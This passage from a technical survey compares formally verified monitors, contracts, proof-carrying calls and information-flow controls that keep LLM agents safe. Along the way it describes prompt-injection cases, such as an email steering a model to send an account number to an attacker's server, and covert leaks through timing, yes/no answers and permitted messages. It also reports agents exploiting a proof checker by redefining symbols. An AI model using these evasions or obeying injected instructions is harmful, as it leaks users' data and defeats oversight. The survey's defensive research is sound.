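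A policy can only forbid what the events record. In this example, a network event includes the destination, port, protocol, method and size, but not the page's path or the request's content. The monitor refuses the fifth request because it is a POST, and cannot see the attack it contains. The same attack written into the address of a GET request would pass, and so would a GET request for a badly designed page that deletes a record when opened. An engineer can add more fields, but the code that fills them in must then be correct too.

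In the scope clause, "subdomains of example.com" might include a name that points to another company's server, so David and colleagues have a compiler translate the pattern into specific network addresses and ports under a fixed policy.

They prove a soundness theorem: for every finite sequence of attempted events, the events the monitor admits satisfy the contract. The proof is a short induction. The empty trace satisfies the contract. If the trace so far satisfies it, a refusal leaves the trace unchanged, and an admission adds an event that has just passed all five clauses. The theorem involves no secrets, so it holds even against an attacker with unlimited computing power. Because the logic is so simple, most of the risk in a deployment is that the monitor might not receive a correct record of every effect before it happens.

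Checking tools in advance can't fully replace this monitor. For tools written in a general-purpose programming language, no algorithm can decide for every tool whether it will ever attempt a forbidden effect, because such an algorithm would solve the halting problem. Checking a single event is easier, and if the monitor keeps running totals, the core check doesn't slow down as the trace grows.

Such contracts can also be combined. Suppose the security firm has its own limit of 5,000 requests per client. The combined contract permits only the targets and effects that both contracts permit, forbids whatever either one forbids, and uses the lower budget. David and colleagues prove that any trace satisfying the combined contract satisfies both originals, provided both count costs and declare information flows the same way.

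These contracts use no history except the running totals, so they can't require a manager's approval before a refund. *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) expresses such rules in a temporal logic, which has operators for "always", "eventually" and "until". Its system, ContrAgent, turns each rule into a small state machine that advances with every call. For the refund rule, the machine blocks refunds until an approval has occurred.

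A rule that the agent must message the customer after every refund is a liveness property, so blocking calls can't enforce it. ContrAgent leaves such a duty pending during the session and records a failure if the session ends without the message. Xiao and colleagues also separate what the agent must do from what its environment must supply, such as valid authorisation data from a policy service, so an operator can tell whether the agent or its environment failed.

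Trace contracts suit tasks where the limits apply to a whole session and the contract's author can list the permitted effects in advance. SecureClaw's policy engine could check such a contract at the preview step, but the engineer would have to decide when to count an action against the budget. If the engine counted only completed actions, a model with one request left could obtain two approvals and then commit both. Counting actions at approval avoids this because the first approval uses up the remaining request.

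### A proof with every call

With both of these forms, the policy author specifies which actions are permitted and must also make sure that those actions can't lead to harm. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) instead has the policy author write down what must stay true, and requires the agent to prove that each call keeps it true. It adapts proof-carrying code, a 1990s technique in which a program arrives with a proof of its own safety for the recipient to check. The proof is a formal derivation that a small program can verify. *Proof-Carrying Agent Actions* (Wang, 2026) uses "proof" to mean receipts and audit evidence, which don't establish anything mathematically.

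In the running example, a family hires a travel agency's agent to arrange a three-night trip and a visa. The family can't inspect the agent, which knows that one hotel pays the agency a commission. Three clauses must hold at every moment:

- Spending commitments, including fees, stay within 2,000 euros.
- The passport goes only to the consulate.
- Every booked hotel has a recorded rating of at least 7 out of 10, from a language model and prompt that both parties fixed when they signed.

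A trusted program called the Airlock holds the passport, a separate 300-euro payment for the agency, and the only access to the tools. For every tool, the contract includes a model of all the states that could occur during a call, including failures, partial results and changes that others make meanwhile. When the agent requests a call, the Airlock uses these models to form the obligation, which is the statement that the agent must prove:

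For every state that fits what the agent can see and satisfies the clauses, the tool's model allows at least one outcome, and every outcome it allows satisfies the clauses.

The contract can hide part of the state from the agent, such as the contents of the passport, so the obligation covers every state that fits. Part (a) is needed because part (b) would be trivially true for any call the model didn't cover, since that call would have no modelled outcomes to check.

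For a payment of q euros, the obligation reduces to b + q ≤ 2,000, where b is the amount already committed. The payment tool records the maximum possible charge before it sends the request to the payment provider, so a later fee can't push the total over the limit, as long as the provider charges no more than that maximum.

Ciliberto and colleagues follow an untrustworthy agent through this contract. It tries to book the hotel that pays the commission, but the hotel has no rating, so the obligation is false and the agent can't prove it. The agent asks for a rating and gets a 5, and asking again returns the same recorded 5. It then tries another hotel, which gets an 8, and books the first night for 900 euros. When an email tells the agent to send the passport to an unknown address, the Airlock rejects the call because the address isn't the consulate's. The agent also asks for its 300 euros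 too early, but that call needs a proof that the trip is booked and the visa granted, so it succeeds only once both are true.

The Airlock has to form the obligation itself, since an agent that supplied its own statement could prove something irrelevant. Even then, a submitted file could redefine a symbol so that the obligation means "true". Ciliberto and colleagues note that agents have exploited a submission system for the proof checker Lean in this way.

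Bookings and prices can also change while the agent looks for a proof. Meanwhile, the Airlock carries out regular control steps, such as closing the contract at its deadline. The agent states how many of these steps may pass before its call runs, and its proof must cover every state those steps could lead to.

Under the compliance theorem, the clauses hold at every moment from the start of the contract until it closes, whatever requests and proofs the agent submits. The proof is by induction over the Airlock's operations. Suppose the clauses hold when an operation begins. If the operation is a control step, a certificate that the Airlock checked at the start shows that the step preserves them. If it is a call, the Airlock has accepted a proof of the obligation, and the actual state is one of those the obligation covers. The tool's model includes everything that can happen during the call,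 so the clauses hold throughout it and when the next operation begins. The argument therefore covers moments that a check between calls would miss, such as when a payment has gone out but no confirmation has come back.

In an example from Ciliberto and colleagues, a policy author protects the budget for a three-night trip by capping each night at 600 euros. The cap is safe because the trip can cost at most 1,800 euros, but it rules out nights at 900, 500 and 500 euros, which total 1,900 and are also within budget. Proof-carrying contracts move the work of staying within budget from the policy author to the agent, which can choose those nights and prove that each booking respects the budget as it goes.

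The example understates what policies can do, because an alignment contract that keeps a running total would also admit all three bookings. Ciliberto and colleagues prove, more generally, that any safe rule based on the same information admits only calls whose obligation is true. Where no algorithm can decide every obligation, any such rule that a program can evaluate by itself must refuse some safe calls, although a program can still check a proof it is given. Proofs therefore have the largest advantage over policies when tools have many possible outcomes and interact in ways that a policy writer would struggle to foresee.

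The author still has to write correct clauses and tool models, but no longer has to derive a rule for each action and prove that the rule is safe. Instead, the agent has to find a proof for each call, and if it can't find one before the window closes, the call doesn't run. The family might lose a booking, but the clauses would still hold. Lean's automation can handle simple obligations such as the budget sum, but Ciliberto and colleagues haven't measured how often agents find harder proofs in time, or at what cost.

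This form suits agreements between parties who don't trust each other's agents, and goals an agent could reach by many plans. For an assistant that sends one type of email, approving each request is much simpler.

### Errors that the policy allows

None of these guarantees rules out errors that the policy allows. A hijacked model can request something that the policy engine will approve, stay within the scope and budget of a trace contract, or attach a valid proof. Ciliberto and colleagues give the example of a travel contract that requires a flight and a hotel but doesn't require their dates to match, so every call could satisfy the contract and the trip would still be useless. David and colleagues note that their monitor enforces the contract as written and can't correct its author's mistakes.

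The usual reply is to make the policy more specific. Ma and Schmid suggest binding each approval more closely to the recipient, the object and the phase of the task. Suppose a policy lets the invoice assistant send any of 2,000 files to any of 500 employees, a million combinations in all. If the recipient must be the approver listed in the company's records for vendor A, 2,000 combinations remain. If the file must also be the invoice that the user selected for this task, only one remains. The policy can also allow sending only from when the user starts an approval until the invoice has gone out, so that text planted in a later document can't trigger another email. SecureClaw's theorem covers these stricter policies without a new proof, as long as the serialized request includes the extra fields.

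The narrowing works only if the extra values come from a trusted source. A hijacked model can fill in the wrong approver, for example, so that name has to come from the company's records or the user. Somebody also has to write a policy this specific for each task, a difficulty that Christodorescu and colleagues raised about deterministic monitors in general. Ciliberto and colleagues propose that AI systems help by drafting the clauses and searching for unwanted outcomes that the clauses allow, such as the trip with mismatched dates, but they haven't tested this.

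Even a very specific policy leaves the model some freedom if the model writes any of the text. For example, it could send the right invoice to the right approver with a note saying "already checked, please pay today". A fixed template for the note would prevent that, but it would also stop the model from explaining anything unusual about the invoice.

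## Stating what the agent can learn and leak

A guarantee about an agent's actions doesn't ensure that it keeps secrets. A hijacked invoice assistant that can email only approved recipients can still pass on what it has read, for example in a note to the approver or a message to another agent. Noninterference, which requires that nothing an observer receives depends on the secret, would rule this out, but it also rules out many useful agents. For example, the calendar assistant from Dongol sends its user's free times to anyone who requests a meeting. Its replies violate noninterference because they depend on the calendar, even though the user wants them sent.

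Researchers have therefore proposed weaker guarantees. Under the strictest, the model's side receives only handles to the data. Others allow the release of a declared summary, any flow to people authorized to read the data, or whatever the task would disclose without an attack.

### Handles only

Ma and Schmid's second theorem covers a version of SecureClaw in which the gateway returns a handle and some routine metadata but no summary. In the theorem's game, the attacker controls the model and the driving loop. The data store holds one of two values behind a handle, say an invoice for $4,200 or one for $9,900. The attacker can request other reads, pass handles around and try to guess new ones, and it wins if it can tell which value the store holds.

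Under the theorem, the attacker can still learn the handles it receives, the type of each value, expiry times, the policy engine's decisions and the fixed refusal messages. The theorem therefore doesn't cover leaks through those decisions, such as when a rule that blocks invoices above $5,000 reveals whether an invoice is over that amount.

The proof uses a simulator, a program that produces everything the attacker would see without using the stored value. If the attacker can't tell the simulator from the real system, the real system has revealed nothing about the value beyond the listed items. The argument has three steps.

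1. Replace the handles, which the gateway computes with a secret key, with random strings. This changes the attacker's chances by at most ε_hid, which measures how well an efficient program can tell the keyed function's output from random strings.
2. Remove the stored value. The attacker's view stays the same unless it guesses a live handle that it never received and gets a trusted component to look up the value.
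3. Bound the chance of such a guess. If handles have κ bits and N_live of them are valid at once, each guess succeeds with probability at most N_live/2^κ. The attacker makes at most q_h guesses.

The attacker's advantage is therefore at most

min(1, q_h · N_live / 2^κ) + ε_hid

With 10^9 guesses, 10^4 live handles and κ = 128, the first term is about 3 × 10^-26. With 64-bit handles, the same attacker would have a chance of up to about 5 in 10 million, and with 32-bit handles the bound would reach 1. The number of live handles matters because the attacker needs to guess only one of them.

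A failed guess must also return only a refusal. If the system answered "expired" for some guesses and "unknown" for others, the attacker would learn which handles had once existed, and the simulator couldn't reproduce those answers.

This theorem limits where the raw invoice can be, but who may receive it depends on the executor's checks. It also describes a fairly limited assistant, because a model with only a handle can forward an invoice to a known approver but can't choose the approver by the amount. Ma and Schmid use the handle-only version as a reference case. They ran their benchmarks with summaries because many of the tasks require the model to read something.

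### A summary with a measured leak

Once the gateway also returns a summary, the model learns something about the invoice by design. How much it learns depends on how different the summaries of two invoices can be. Ma and Schmid measure this with total variation distance. If P and Q are the probability distributions of the summaries for two values, then

Δ(P, Q) = ½ Σ |P(x) − Q(x)|

where the sum covers every possible summary x. The distance is 0 if the two distributions are identical and 1 if no summary can come from both. It is also the most by which an attacker's chance of giving any particular answer can differ between the two cases. Suppose a summary states whether an invoice exceeds $5,000, and is right 75% of the time. For one invoice above the limit and one below it, Δ is ½ × (0.5 + 0.5) = 0.5.

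The third theorem covers an attacker that makes several reads. For each read there are two candidate values, a left one and a right one, and a single hidden coin decides whether the attacker gets summaries of all the left values or all the right ones. Its advantage is at most

min(1, Δ₁ + Δ₂ + … + Δ_m) + 2 × (the handle bound above)

The proof switches the summaries from the left case to the right case one at a time, and switching the i-th one changes the attacker's chances by at most Δ_i. The handle bound counts twice because the simulator must replace the real system in both cases. The sum can overstate the leak. After two reads of the noisy summary above, the sum is 1, but the attacker's real advantage is still 0.5.

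The core of SecureClaw's summary program is deterministic, so Δ is always 0 or 1. For invoices of $4,200 and $9,900, the summaries contain "$4.2k" and "$9.9k", so one read gives Δ = 1. The bound is then trivial, since no attacker's advantage can exceed 1. This is as it should be, because the attacker can read the amount. If two invoices differ only in the account number, which the program replaces with a token, Δ is 0 and the attacker can only guess handles.

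So under the theorem, invoices with identical summaries effectively form a group, and the attacker learns only which group an invoice belongs to. A contract can state this directly, for example as a guarantee that the model can't tell apart two invoices that differ only in their account numbers.

Ma and Schmid tested the summary program on 122 pairs of inputs, each of which differed in one sensitive place.

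| What differs within the pair | Pairs | Δ |
|---|---|---|
| Email addresses, account numbers, web addresses and similar identifiers | 55 | 0 |
| Content that the program cuts off or removes | 32 | 0 |
| Free text within the first 512 characters | 12 | 1 |
| One of the first eight items in a list | 8 | 1 |
| Subject line | 6 | 1 |
| Name of the other party to a transaction, in plain text | 6 | 1 |
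| Malformed identifier that the program doesn't recognise | 3 | 1 |

The mean is 0.287, because the summaries differed in 35 of the 122 pairs. Ma and Schmid point out that it is not a bound on the leak. The mean depends on how many pairs of each kind they happened to include, and twelve more free-text pairs would have raised it to 0.35. An attacker who wants a subject line gets Δ = 1 every time. A contract that stated a maximum advantage of 0.287 per read would be wrong for all 35 pairs whose summaries differed.

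The theorem also assumes that no information about a secret carries over from one read to the next, except in the summaries. The program therefore resets its tokens for each read. If it kept numbering email addresses across reads, a token in the second summary could reveal something about the first document. Rewriting a summary afterwards, even with a language model, can't increase Δ if the rewriter uses nothing about the secret except the summary. This follows from a standard result called the data-processing inequality.

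A hijacked model can pass on anything in a summary, including to other agents. It still can't fetch the raw invoice or send an unapproved email, but the theorem doesn't restrict where the invoice amount goes next.

### Labels that follow the data

Information-flow control restricts what an agent can learn and leak by attaching labels to data and updating them as the data moves. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that gives each piece of data two labels.

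The confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the data. When the agent combines two sources, only people in both sets may read the result. If Ana, Ben and Chloe may read the invoice, and Ben, Chloe and Dev may read the contract, then only Ben and Chloe may read a text based on both. The integrity label is either "trusted" or "untrusted", and anything that draws on untrusted data is untrusted. FIDES gives the model's output the combined labels of everything in its context.

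Before each tool call, a policy engine checks the labels against two rules:

- **Trusted action:** a consequential call may go ahead only if the decision to make it, and its arguments, are based on trusted data. A policy can relax this for some arguments, such as the body of a message.
- **Permitted flow:** everybody who will receive a piece of data must be in its set of readers.

The second rule limits the damage from prompt injection but doesn't prevent the injection itself. A hijacked model can send the invoice only to people already allowed to read it.

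An agent that applied the first rule naively would do very little. Once the invoice's text enters the context, every later decision is untrusted, so the policy engine blocks the legitimate email along with the malicious one. Costa and colleagues found that, without any attack, these checks cut a basic agent's completion rate on AgentDojo's office tasks from 75% to 37%.

FIDES reached 59% with the checks on, because it keeps untrusted data out of the context. If a tool's result would change the context's label, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model can then output a request to send the variable to the approver, and FIDES treats that decision as trusted even though the variable's content is untrusted.

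When a task depends on the content, FIDES passes the variable to a second language model, called a quarantined model, which has no tools, and stores the answer in a new variable. The main model can inspect the answer if it needs it to choose the next step. To limit what an attacker can do with the answer, FIDES can restrict its type to yes or no, or to a fixed list of options, and record the type in the label. For example, if the user asks the agent to add any meeting requests to the calendar, the quarantined model first answers whether an email contains one. If it does, a second query extracts the details straight into a variable for the calendar tool.

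The policy can treat a yes-or-no answer as safe because it carries only one bit, but fourteen such answers are enough to encode any whole-dollar amount up to $16,383. A contract that makes this exception for secret data should also limit the number of answers.

Costa and colleagues show that label tracking enforces a property called explicit secrecy. Any path, meaning a sequence of steps the agent could follow, acts on stored data as a function g. The path satisfies explicit secrecy if, for any two initial stores d₁ and d₂ that look the same to the attacker, g(d₁) and g(d₂) also look the same.

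Explicit secrecy never compares two paths. Suppose an agent posts "1" on a public page if the invoice exceeds $5,000 and "0" otherwise. Each path writes a constant, so both satisfy explicit secrecy, yet anyone who visits the page learns whether the invoice exceeds $5,000. The order of tool calls can leak information in the same way, and the definition leaves out timing and the length of network packets. Costa and colleagues accept these leaks because noninterference would forbid almost any publicly visible call after the agent has read a secret.

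FIDES also assumes that the model is not fully compromised. In its threat model, the language model and the code of the driving loop are trusted, and the attacker controls only outside data. The permitted-flow rule should hold even if the model is hostile, as long as the model keeps no hidden memory between calls, because the labels cover anything it could compute from its context. The trusted-action rule would then fail, because a hostile model can start from trusted input alone, and its calls would still count as trusted.

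### Fixing the program first

CaMeL, a system that Google DeepMind published in 2025, restricts the model further by having it write the whole program in advance. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how it works. A privileged model reads the user's request but no untrusted content, and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the plan and makes the tool calls. When the plan needs something from an untrusted document, the interpreter calls a quarantined model, which has no tools, to extract it. Each value has a tag for its sources and a tag for its permitted readers. Before every tool call, a policy function checks the tool, the arguments and their tags, and allows or denies the call.

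*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) classifies CaMeL and FIDES as two versions of the "dual LLM" pattern. In CaMeL, an injection can't add a call to the plan, but it can corrupt a value. For example, if the plan looks up Bob's email address in a chat channel, a planted message could make the quarantined model return the attacker's address. The tag still shows that the address came from an untrusted source, so a policy can block anything from being sent there.

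Nikolaou and colleagues note that CaMeL has no formal verification. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, call for a machine-checked proof of noninterference, with exceptions for approved releases, and list three channels that the tags leave open:

- **Loops:** if a plan fetches a web page once for each unpaid invoice, the page's access log reveals how many there are.
- **Errors:** if a step fails only for certain secret values, the failure reveals something about the value.
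- **Timing:** a step may take longer for some values than for others.

Tallam and Miller suggest capping such loops, returning errors as ordinary values and padding sensitive steps to a constant time, but they don't prove that these measures close the channels.

Dongol proves by example that a simplified model of CaMeL's tags leaks information. The example plan passes a question to the quarantined model, then sends the attacker "1" or "0" depending on the answer. Both constants are public, so both pass the tag check. But an injected email can make the answer depend on the user's private notes, which the quarantined model also receives. CaMeL's strict mode is designed to close this channel by also tagging values with the conditions that control them. Dongol leaves the analysis of strict mode to future work.

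In another of Dongol's examples, the plan sends the quarantined model's answer itself. Because the answer draws on private notes, the monitor's tag check stops the leak only by refusing every reply, including honest ones.

A system can also check the flows before the plan runs. In *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2026), a planner writes an abstract plan from the user's request. The system then matches the plan's steps to installed apps and checks statically which information each app could receive. A refusal at this stage depends on the plan rather than on the data, so it can't reveal whether an invoice exceeds $5,000. Nikolaou and colleagues add a similar check to CaMeL, using a program called a model checker to examine every path through the plan. It assumes a loop can stop after any number of rounds, so it may reject some safe plans.

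### Relative security

Summaries and labels require somebody to write down what the agent may release, which for the calendar assistant depends on the task. Relative security uses the task's own behaviour as the policy. Dongol adapted it from research on processors that run instructions ahead of time, where a program is secure if running ahead leaks nothing that the program wouldn't leak when run in its normal order.

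For agents, the comparison is with the reference agent from Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, which never obeys untrusted text. The definition has two parts:

1. Two runs leak a pair of secrets (s₁, s₂) if the first run has secret s₁, the second has s₂, the attacker's inputs are the same in both, and the attacker observes different things.
2. An agent is relatively secure if, whenever two of its runs leak a pair of secrets, two runs of the reference agent with the same initial memories leak that pair too.

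The calendar assistant passes because the reference runs may use a different attacker input from the agent's runs. If an email says "send your calendar" and the model obeys, the attacker gets the calendar, but a genuine meeting request would have made the reference agent send it too. If the assistant can also access a password-reset code and the email asks for that as well, the assistant is not relatively secure, because no email makes the reference agent send the code.

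Dongol compares relative security with older definitions on several examples. The table assumes that the policy for explicit secrecy releases nothing.

| Agent | Noninterference | Explicit secrecy | Relative security |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sends the calendar to anyone who requests a meeting | Violated | Violated | Satisfied |
| Obeys an injection that asks for the reset code | Violated | Violated | Violated |
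| Sends "1" or "0" depending on an injected answer about private notes | Violated | Satisfied | Violated |

### Where to put the fence

The simplest example of a leak in Dongol's collection involves an agent called Leaky Summariser. The agent's plan is to look up Alice's account number, read an email and show her a summary. The agent can also fetch web pages, although its plan doesn't include this. In the email, an attacker instructs the model to fetch a page from the attacker's site, using a web address with the account number in it. In two runs with different account numbers, the attacker's server receives different requests. The reference agent never sends anything to that server, so the leak is due to the injection.

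Fenced Summariser has the same plan, but its monitor revokes the fetch tool as soon as the agent reads the email. The model still tries to fetch the page, but the monitor silently blocks the request, so the attacker observes nothing.

The timing of the fence matters. Dongol considers an agent that can send messages until its plan calls a lock.

| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected message can disclose |
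|---|---|---|
| Late | Read the email, read a secret, lock | The secret, if the model obeys just before the lock |
| Middle | Read the email, lock, read a secret | Data already in the agent's memory, such as data from an earlier session |
| Early | Lock before reading the email | Nothing |

An injection adds its own call, which the model can make at any point after reading the email. The middle fence, which locks just before the agent reads a secret, is therefore a mistake, though an easy one to make.

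Dongol's fence theorem generalises the early fence. The agent is relatively secure if the monitor revokes every tool an injection can call no later than the first untrusted read, and no trusted input ever grants those tools back. This holds for any plan the agent has and any texts the model treats as instructions. In the proof, the monitor refuses each injected call without changing its own state, while the reference agent waits. Every other step matches the same step of the reference agent.

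The theorem has several restrictions besides its assumptions about the deployment:

- **One call per injection.** Suppose an instruction can be a small program that changes the plan's variables. It could copy a secret over the text that the plan is about to send, and the plan's own message would then carry the secret. A sandbox that discards such changes prevents this, as long as the fence also covers reads.
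- **A schedule fixed in advance.** As elsewhere in PlanTERS, the moment when the model obeys can't depend on a secret or on the monitor's response.
- **No timing.** The attacker sees the content and order of messages, but not when they arrive.
- **Runs that end.** An agent that runs forever needs the extra condition that the model can't keep obeying injections without end.

The ban on granting tools back is awkward for an assistant that processes one email after another. If the monitor restores the tools while an old email is still in the model's context, the model can then follow instructions in that email. Dongol's solution restores the tools only at the start of a fresh session, which must clear everything the model retains from untrusted content.

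A fence on email would stop the invoice assistant from doing its job, as would Schneider's rule against sending after reading a file. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference agent has the same monitor and loses the same ability.

### When the verdict depends on timing

Approvals let an agent use a tool after it has read untrusted text. In Dongol's example, an agent reads an email, Alice approves a reply, and the plan sends it. If her approval covers the next message whatever it contains, an injection can use that approval to send private data. The monitor then refuses Alice's reply because the approval has already been used.

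In Call Approval, Alice approves the exact reply, much as SecureClaw's policy engine approves an exact request. Suppose that, just before the plan sends the reply, the model follows an injected instruction to send some private text.

| | Private text differs from the approved reply | Private text equals the approved reply |
|---|---|---|
| Injected message | The monitor refuses it | The monitor allows it |
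| Planned reply | The monitor allows it | The monitor refuses it, since the approval is used up |
| What the attacker receives | The approved reply | The approved reply, one step earlier |

The agent is relatively secure against an attacker that sees only the content and order of messages, because these are the same in both cases. An attacker that can also time the messages learns whether the private text equals the reply. The agent is not relatively secure against this attacker, because the reference agent always sends the reply at the planned step. A contract that relies on exact approvals for secrecy must therefore specify whether the attacker can measure timing.

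The model without timing also misses some leaks because it compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages between reads. Suppose an injection fetches a permitted page if a secret is 0 and a forbidden page otherwise, and the attacker can see permitted fetches. The attacker sees a fetch only if the secret is 0, but the definition never compares these two runs. Dongol's model with timing detects this leak.

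### What one bit can license

Relative security depends on which secrets an attacker can tell apart with some input, not on how many inputs the attacker would need to learn the whole secret. Suppose an assistant's job is to tell anyone who asks whether a six-digit code is correct. Each answer from the reference agent reveals at most one bit, but an injection makes the hijacked agent send the code itself. The attacker could already have told any two codes apart, such as 111111 and 222222, by asking the reference agent whether the code is 111111. Every leak of the hijacked agent is therefore also a leak of the reference agent, and sending the whole code counts as relatively secure. Yet an attacker who could only ask the reference agent about one code at a time might need hundreds of thousands of questions to find the right one.

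Dongol gives a stricter version, uniform relative security, that closes this gap. It requires a fixed rule, independent of the secret, that turns the attacker's input to the agent into the input for the reference agent. If the rule always gives 111111 as the guess, the reference agent can't tell 222222 from 333333, but the hijacked agent can, so the hijacked agent fails the stricter version. The fence theorem satisfies it, because the theorem's proof matches every run of the agent with a reference run on the same input.

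A sound comparison with the reference agent doesn't limit what the task itself reveals, so Dongol adds a disclosure bound. The engineer chooses a function δ of the secrets and shows that the attacker can't distinguish two reference runs with the same input and the same value of δ. If the agent is relatively secure, the same bound holds for the agent under attack. For the calendar assistant, δ would return the calendar, so the bound rules out leaking the reset code.

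For the code checker, δ has to distinguish every pair of codes, because any two codes give different answers to some question. The bound therefore permits full disclosure of the code. To guarantee a limit on disclosure per question, an engineer has to prove uniform relative security and separately bound what the reference agent reveals in each answer.

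## Listing the assumptions behind each guarantee and checking them

The guarantees in the last two sections depend on conditions that no proof about the design can establish, for example that nobody has left the email password on the wrong machine. A contract is more useful if it lists the assumptions behind each guarantee separately than if it covers them all with one sentence, such as "we assume that the trusted core is secure". Nobody can check an assumption that broad, and when part of it turns out to be false, nobody can tell which guarantees have failed.

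### A separate list for each guarantee

Ma and Schmid group SecureClaw's assumptions by the property they support. The table below keeps their grouping and also separates cryptographic assumptions from operational ones. Its last row covers an optional version that splits the policy engine between two servers so that neither one alone learns the details of the request.

| Guarantee | Cryptographic or statistical assumptions | Operational assumptions |
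|---|---|---|
| **Actions** | Attackers can't forge tags; two requests almost never share a fingerprint | The gateway and executor use the same complete format; each confirmation belongs to one exact request; clocks nearly agree; the executor checks and marks each approval in a single step; every action with an outside effect goes through the executor |
| **Data, handles only** | Attackers can't guess live handles; handles look random | Every sensitive read goes through the gateway; the operator has marked the sensitive fields correctly; a failed guess returns only a refusal; only trusted components can look up a handle |
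| **Data, with summaries** | As above, plus a measured difference between summaries | As above, plus: the summary program is fixed; anything that rewrites a summary has no other information about the secret |
| **Private policy checks** | The two protocols that hide the request are secure | The servers follow the protocols and don't collude; messages have a fixed shape |

When each guarantee has its own list of assumptions, an engineer can work out which guarantees a failed assumption affects. Suppose the accounts department adds bank details to its invoices and the operator doesn't mark the new field as sensitive. The gateway then passes the bank details to the model, and the data guarantee doesn't cover them. The action guarantee still holds, because none of its assumptions depend on how the operator marked the fields.

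If a developer leaves the driving loop with a second connection that can only send email, the action guarantee fails but the data guarantee still holds. An attacker could email out the summaries, since the model has those, but not the raw invoice.

Ma and Schmid also state that their theorems don't require the model to be honest, a filter to catch malicious prompts, or the summaries to be perfect. Listing these helps a reader who is used to defences that depend on all three.

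### Numbers and yes-or-no conditions

A cryptographic assumption adds a term to the bound, and the engineer can usually shrink that term by choosing longer keys or fingerprints. Operational assumptions don't appear in the bound, but the theorem holds only if they are met. For example, it doesn't apply at all if the executor checks an approval in one step and marks it as used in another.

A tiny bound is therefore weak evidence about the total risk. Suppose the cryptographic terms add up to one in 10^50, and the engineer thinks there is a one-in-fifty chance that the team has overlooked a route to the email service. The chance that the action guarantee fails is then about one in fifty, and longer fingerprints wouldn't change it.

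An operational assumption can also fail in some tasks even when its overall score is good. In an audit by Ma and Schmid, a detector found 99.2% of the protected fields but missed at least one in 117 of 996 tasks, so the assumption of correct marking was false for those tasks.

The design affects which operational assumptions the contract needs. For example, the bound on an attacker's chance of guessing a valid handle depends on the number of guesses. With 10,000 live handles of 64 bits each, an attacker needs about 1.8 billion guesses for a one-in-a-million chance of success, which takes about half an hour at a million guesses per second. The contract would then have to list a limit on the guessing rate, and someone would have to enforce it. With 128-bit handles, the same attacker would need about 10^15 years to reach the same chance of success, so the contract can leave the limit out.

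The games behind SecureClaw's theorems begin by choosing random secret keys, so the guarantees also depend on the deployed keys being random and staying secret. If a developer prints a deployed key in a log file, an attacker who reads the log can forge tags or compute fingerprints directly, and the theorems' bounds no longer apply.

The replay check depends on the executor marking each approval as used before sending the payment. If the executor crashes between the two steps, the payment doesn't go out and somebody has to approve it again. If it sent the payment first, a crash could leave the payment completed but the approval unmarked, and the attacker could submit the approval again.

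Preventing replay also depends on accurate clocks. Suppose approvals are valid for five minutes, a database deletes each used identifier after five minutes, and the executor's clock then falls three minutes behind. Between minutes five and eight, the executor still accepts the approval as recent, but the database no longer shows that it was used, so an attacker could replay it. Keeping identifiers for longer than the validity period plus the largest possible clock error prevents this.

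### Four versions of complete mediation

All the systems in this comparison assume that nothing important bypasses the monitor, but they define this differently.

| System | What must hold | What it leaves to other assumptions or defences |
|---|---|---|
| SecureClaw: complete mediation | Every action with an outside effect goes through the executor, and every sensitive read goes through the gateway | Whether the approved request describes everything the action will do |
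| Alignment contracts: Effect Observability Assumption | Every network, file or program effect has a correct event, and the monitor handles it before it happens | Information hidden in permitted content or in timing |
| Containment Verification: effect exclusivity | Every externally visible effect goes through the typed action interface and has an event in the model | Bugs in Python, the operating system, the sandbox or the hardware |
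| Proof-carrying contracts: isolation of the agent | The agent changes nothing except through calls that the Airlock selects, and can't influence a call that is already running | Misbehaviour by outside services and other people |

David and colleagues break their version into three obligations, which an engineer can check separately. Every effect must produce a correct event, every event must reach the monitor early enough for the monitor to block the effect, and the event must declare every flow of information that the contract covers. For example, a system that accurately logs each request just after sending it meets the first obligation but fails the second.

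Moon and Varshney's theorem covers events in the model. A corollary extends it to real effects under the assumption of effect exclusivity, which requires every real effect to have such an event. General-purpose tools make this difficult. If one of the typed actions is "run this shell command", the command can send an email, delete a file and open a connection, and a single "command run" event doesn't represent any of these effects.

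Isolation also covers a subtler attack. Suppose a tool checks a request to email a file, then reads the file from a folder the agent can edit. The agent replaces the file between the check and the read. A rule that only requires emails to go through the right tool would not prevent this, because the email still does. SecureClaw prevents it by including the file's version in the approved request. Ciliberto and colleagues rule it out in their definition of isolation, which lets a tool receive only one fixed input from the agent.

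### The layer at which the monitor works

A monitor can enforce only rules about things it can see. The contract for testing a client's websites permits GET and HEAD requests and forbids POST, but a kernel hook usually can't enforce that rule. A kernel hook is a small program that the operating system runs whenever an application opens a connection, reads a file or starts another program. Most web traffic uses TLS encryption, and an application normally encrypts a request before handing it to the operating system. The hook can then see the destination address, the port and the amount of data, but not whether the request is a GET or a POST.

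A kernel hook can therefore enforce the rule about destinations but not the rule about methods. David and colleagues require this contract's monitor to run where it can still read the method, such as in a wrapper around the web tool, in the browser, or in a proxy that handles the requests. Kernel hooks are still suitable for the rules about local files and programs.

Wrappers can also miss forbidden requests. In the same example, a permitted page redirects to admin.example-corp.com, which is out of scope. Many web libraries follow redirects automatically, so if the wrapper checks only the agent's original request, the library will make the forbidden one. The wrapper has to turn off automatic redirects or check each one. An agent that can run its own code could also bypass the wrapper by opening a connection directly.

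Higher layers have more information about a request, and lower layers are harder to bypass, so a deployment usually needs both. For example, a firewall can block every connection except those to the proxy, and the proxy can check each request's method. Moon and Varshney recommend running a verified framework inside a sandbox to limit the damage if something bypasses the framework. They also warn against relying on the sandbox alone, citing Copy Fail, a Linux privilege-escalation flaw that went unnoticed for nearly a decade.

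SecureClaw's executor doesn't have this visibility problem for email, because it itself builds the request to the email service and can read the recipient before the request is encrypted.

### The seven assumptions of a proof-carrying contract

Ciliberto and colleagues give an unusually complete list of the assumptions that must hold for a proof to ensure a safe outcome. The examples in the table come from the family's travel contract, which has a budget of 2,000 euros.

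| Assumption | What must hold | Example of a failure |
|---|---|---|
| **A1. Sound checking** | Every statement that the proof checker accepts is true | A bug lets through a false proof that a payment fits the budget |
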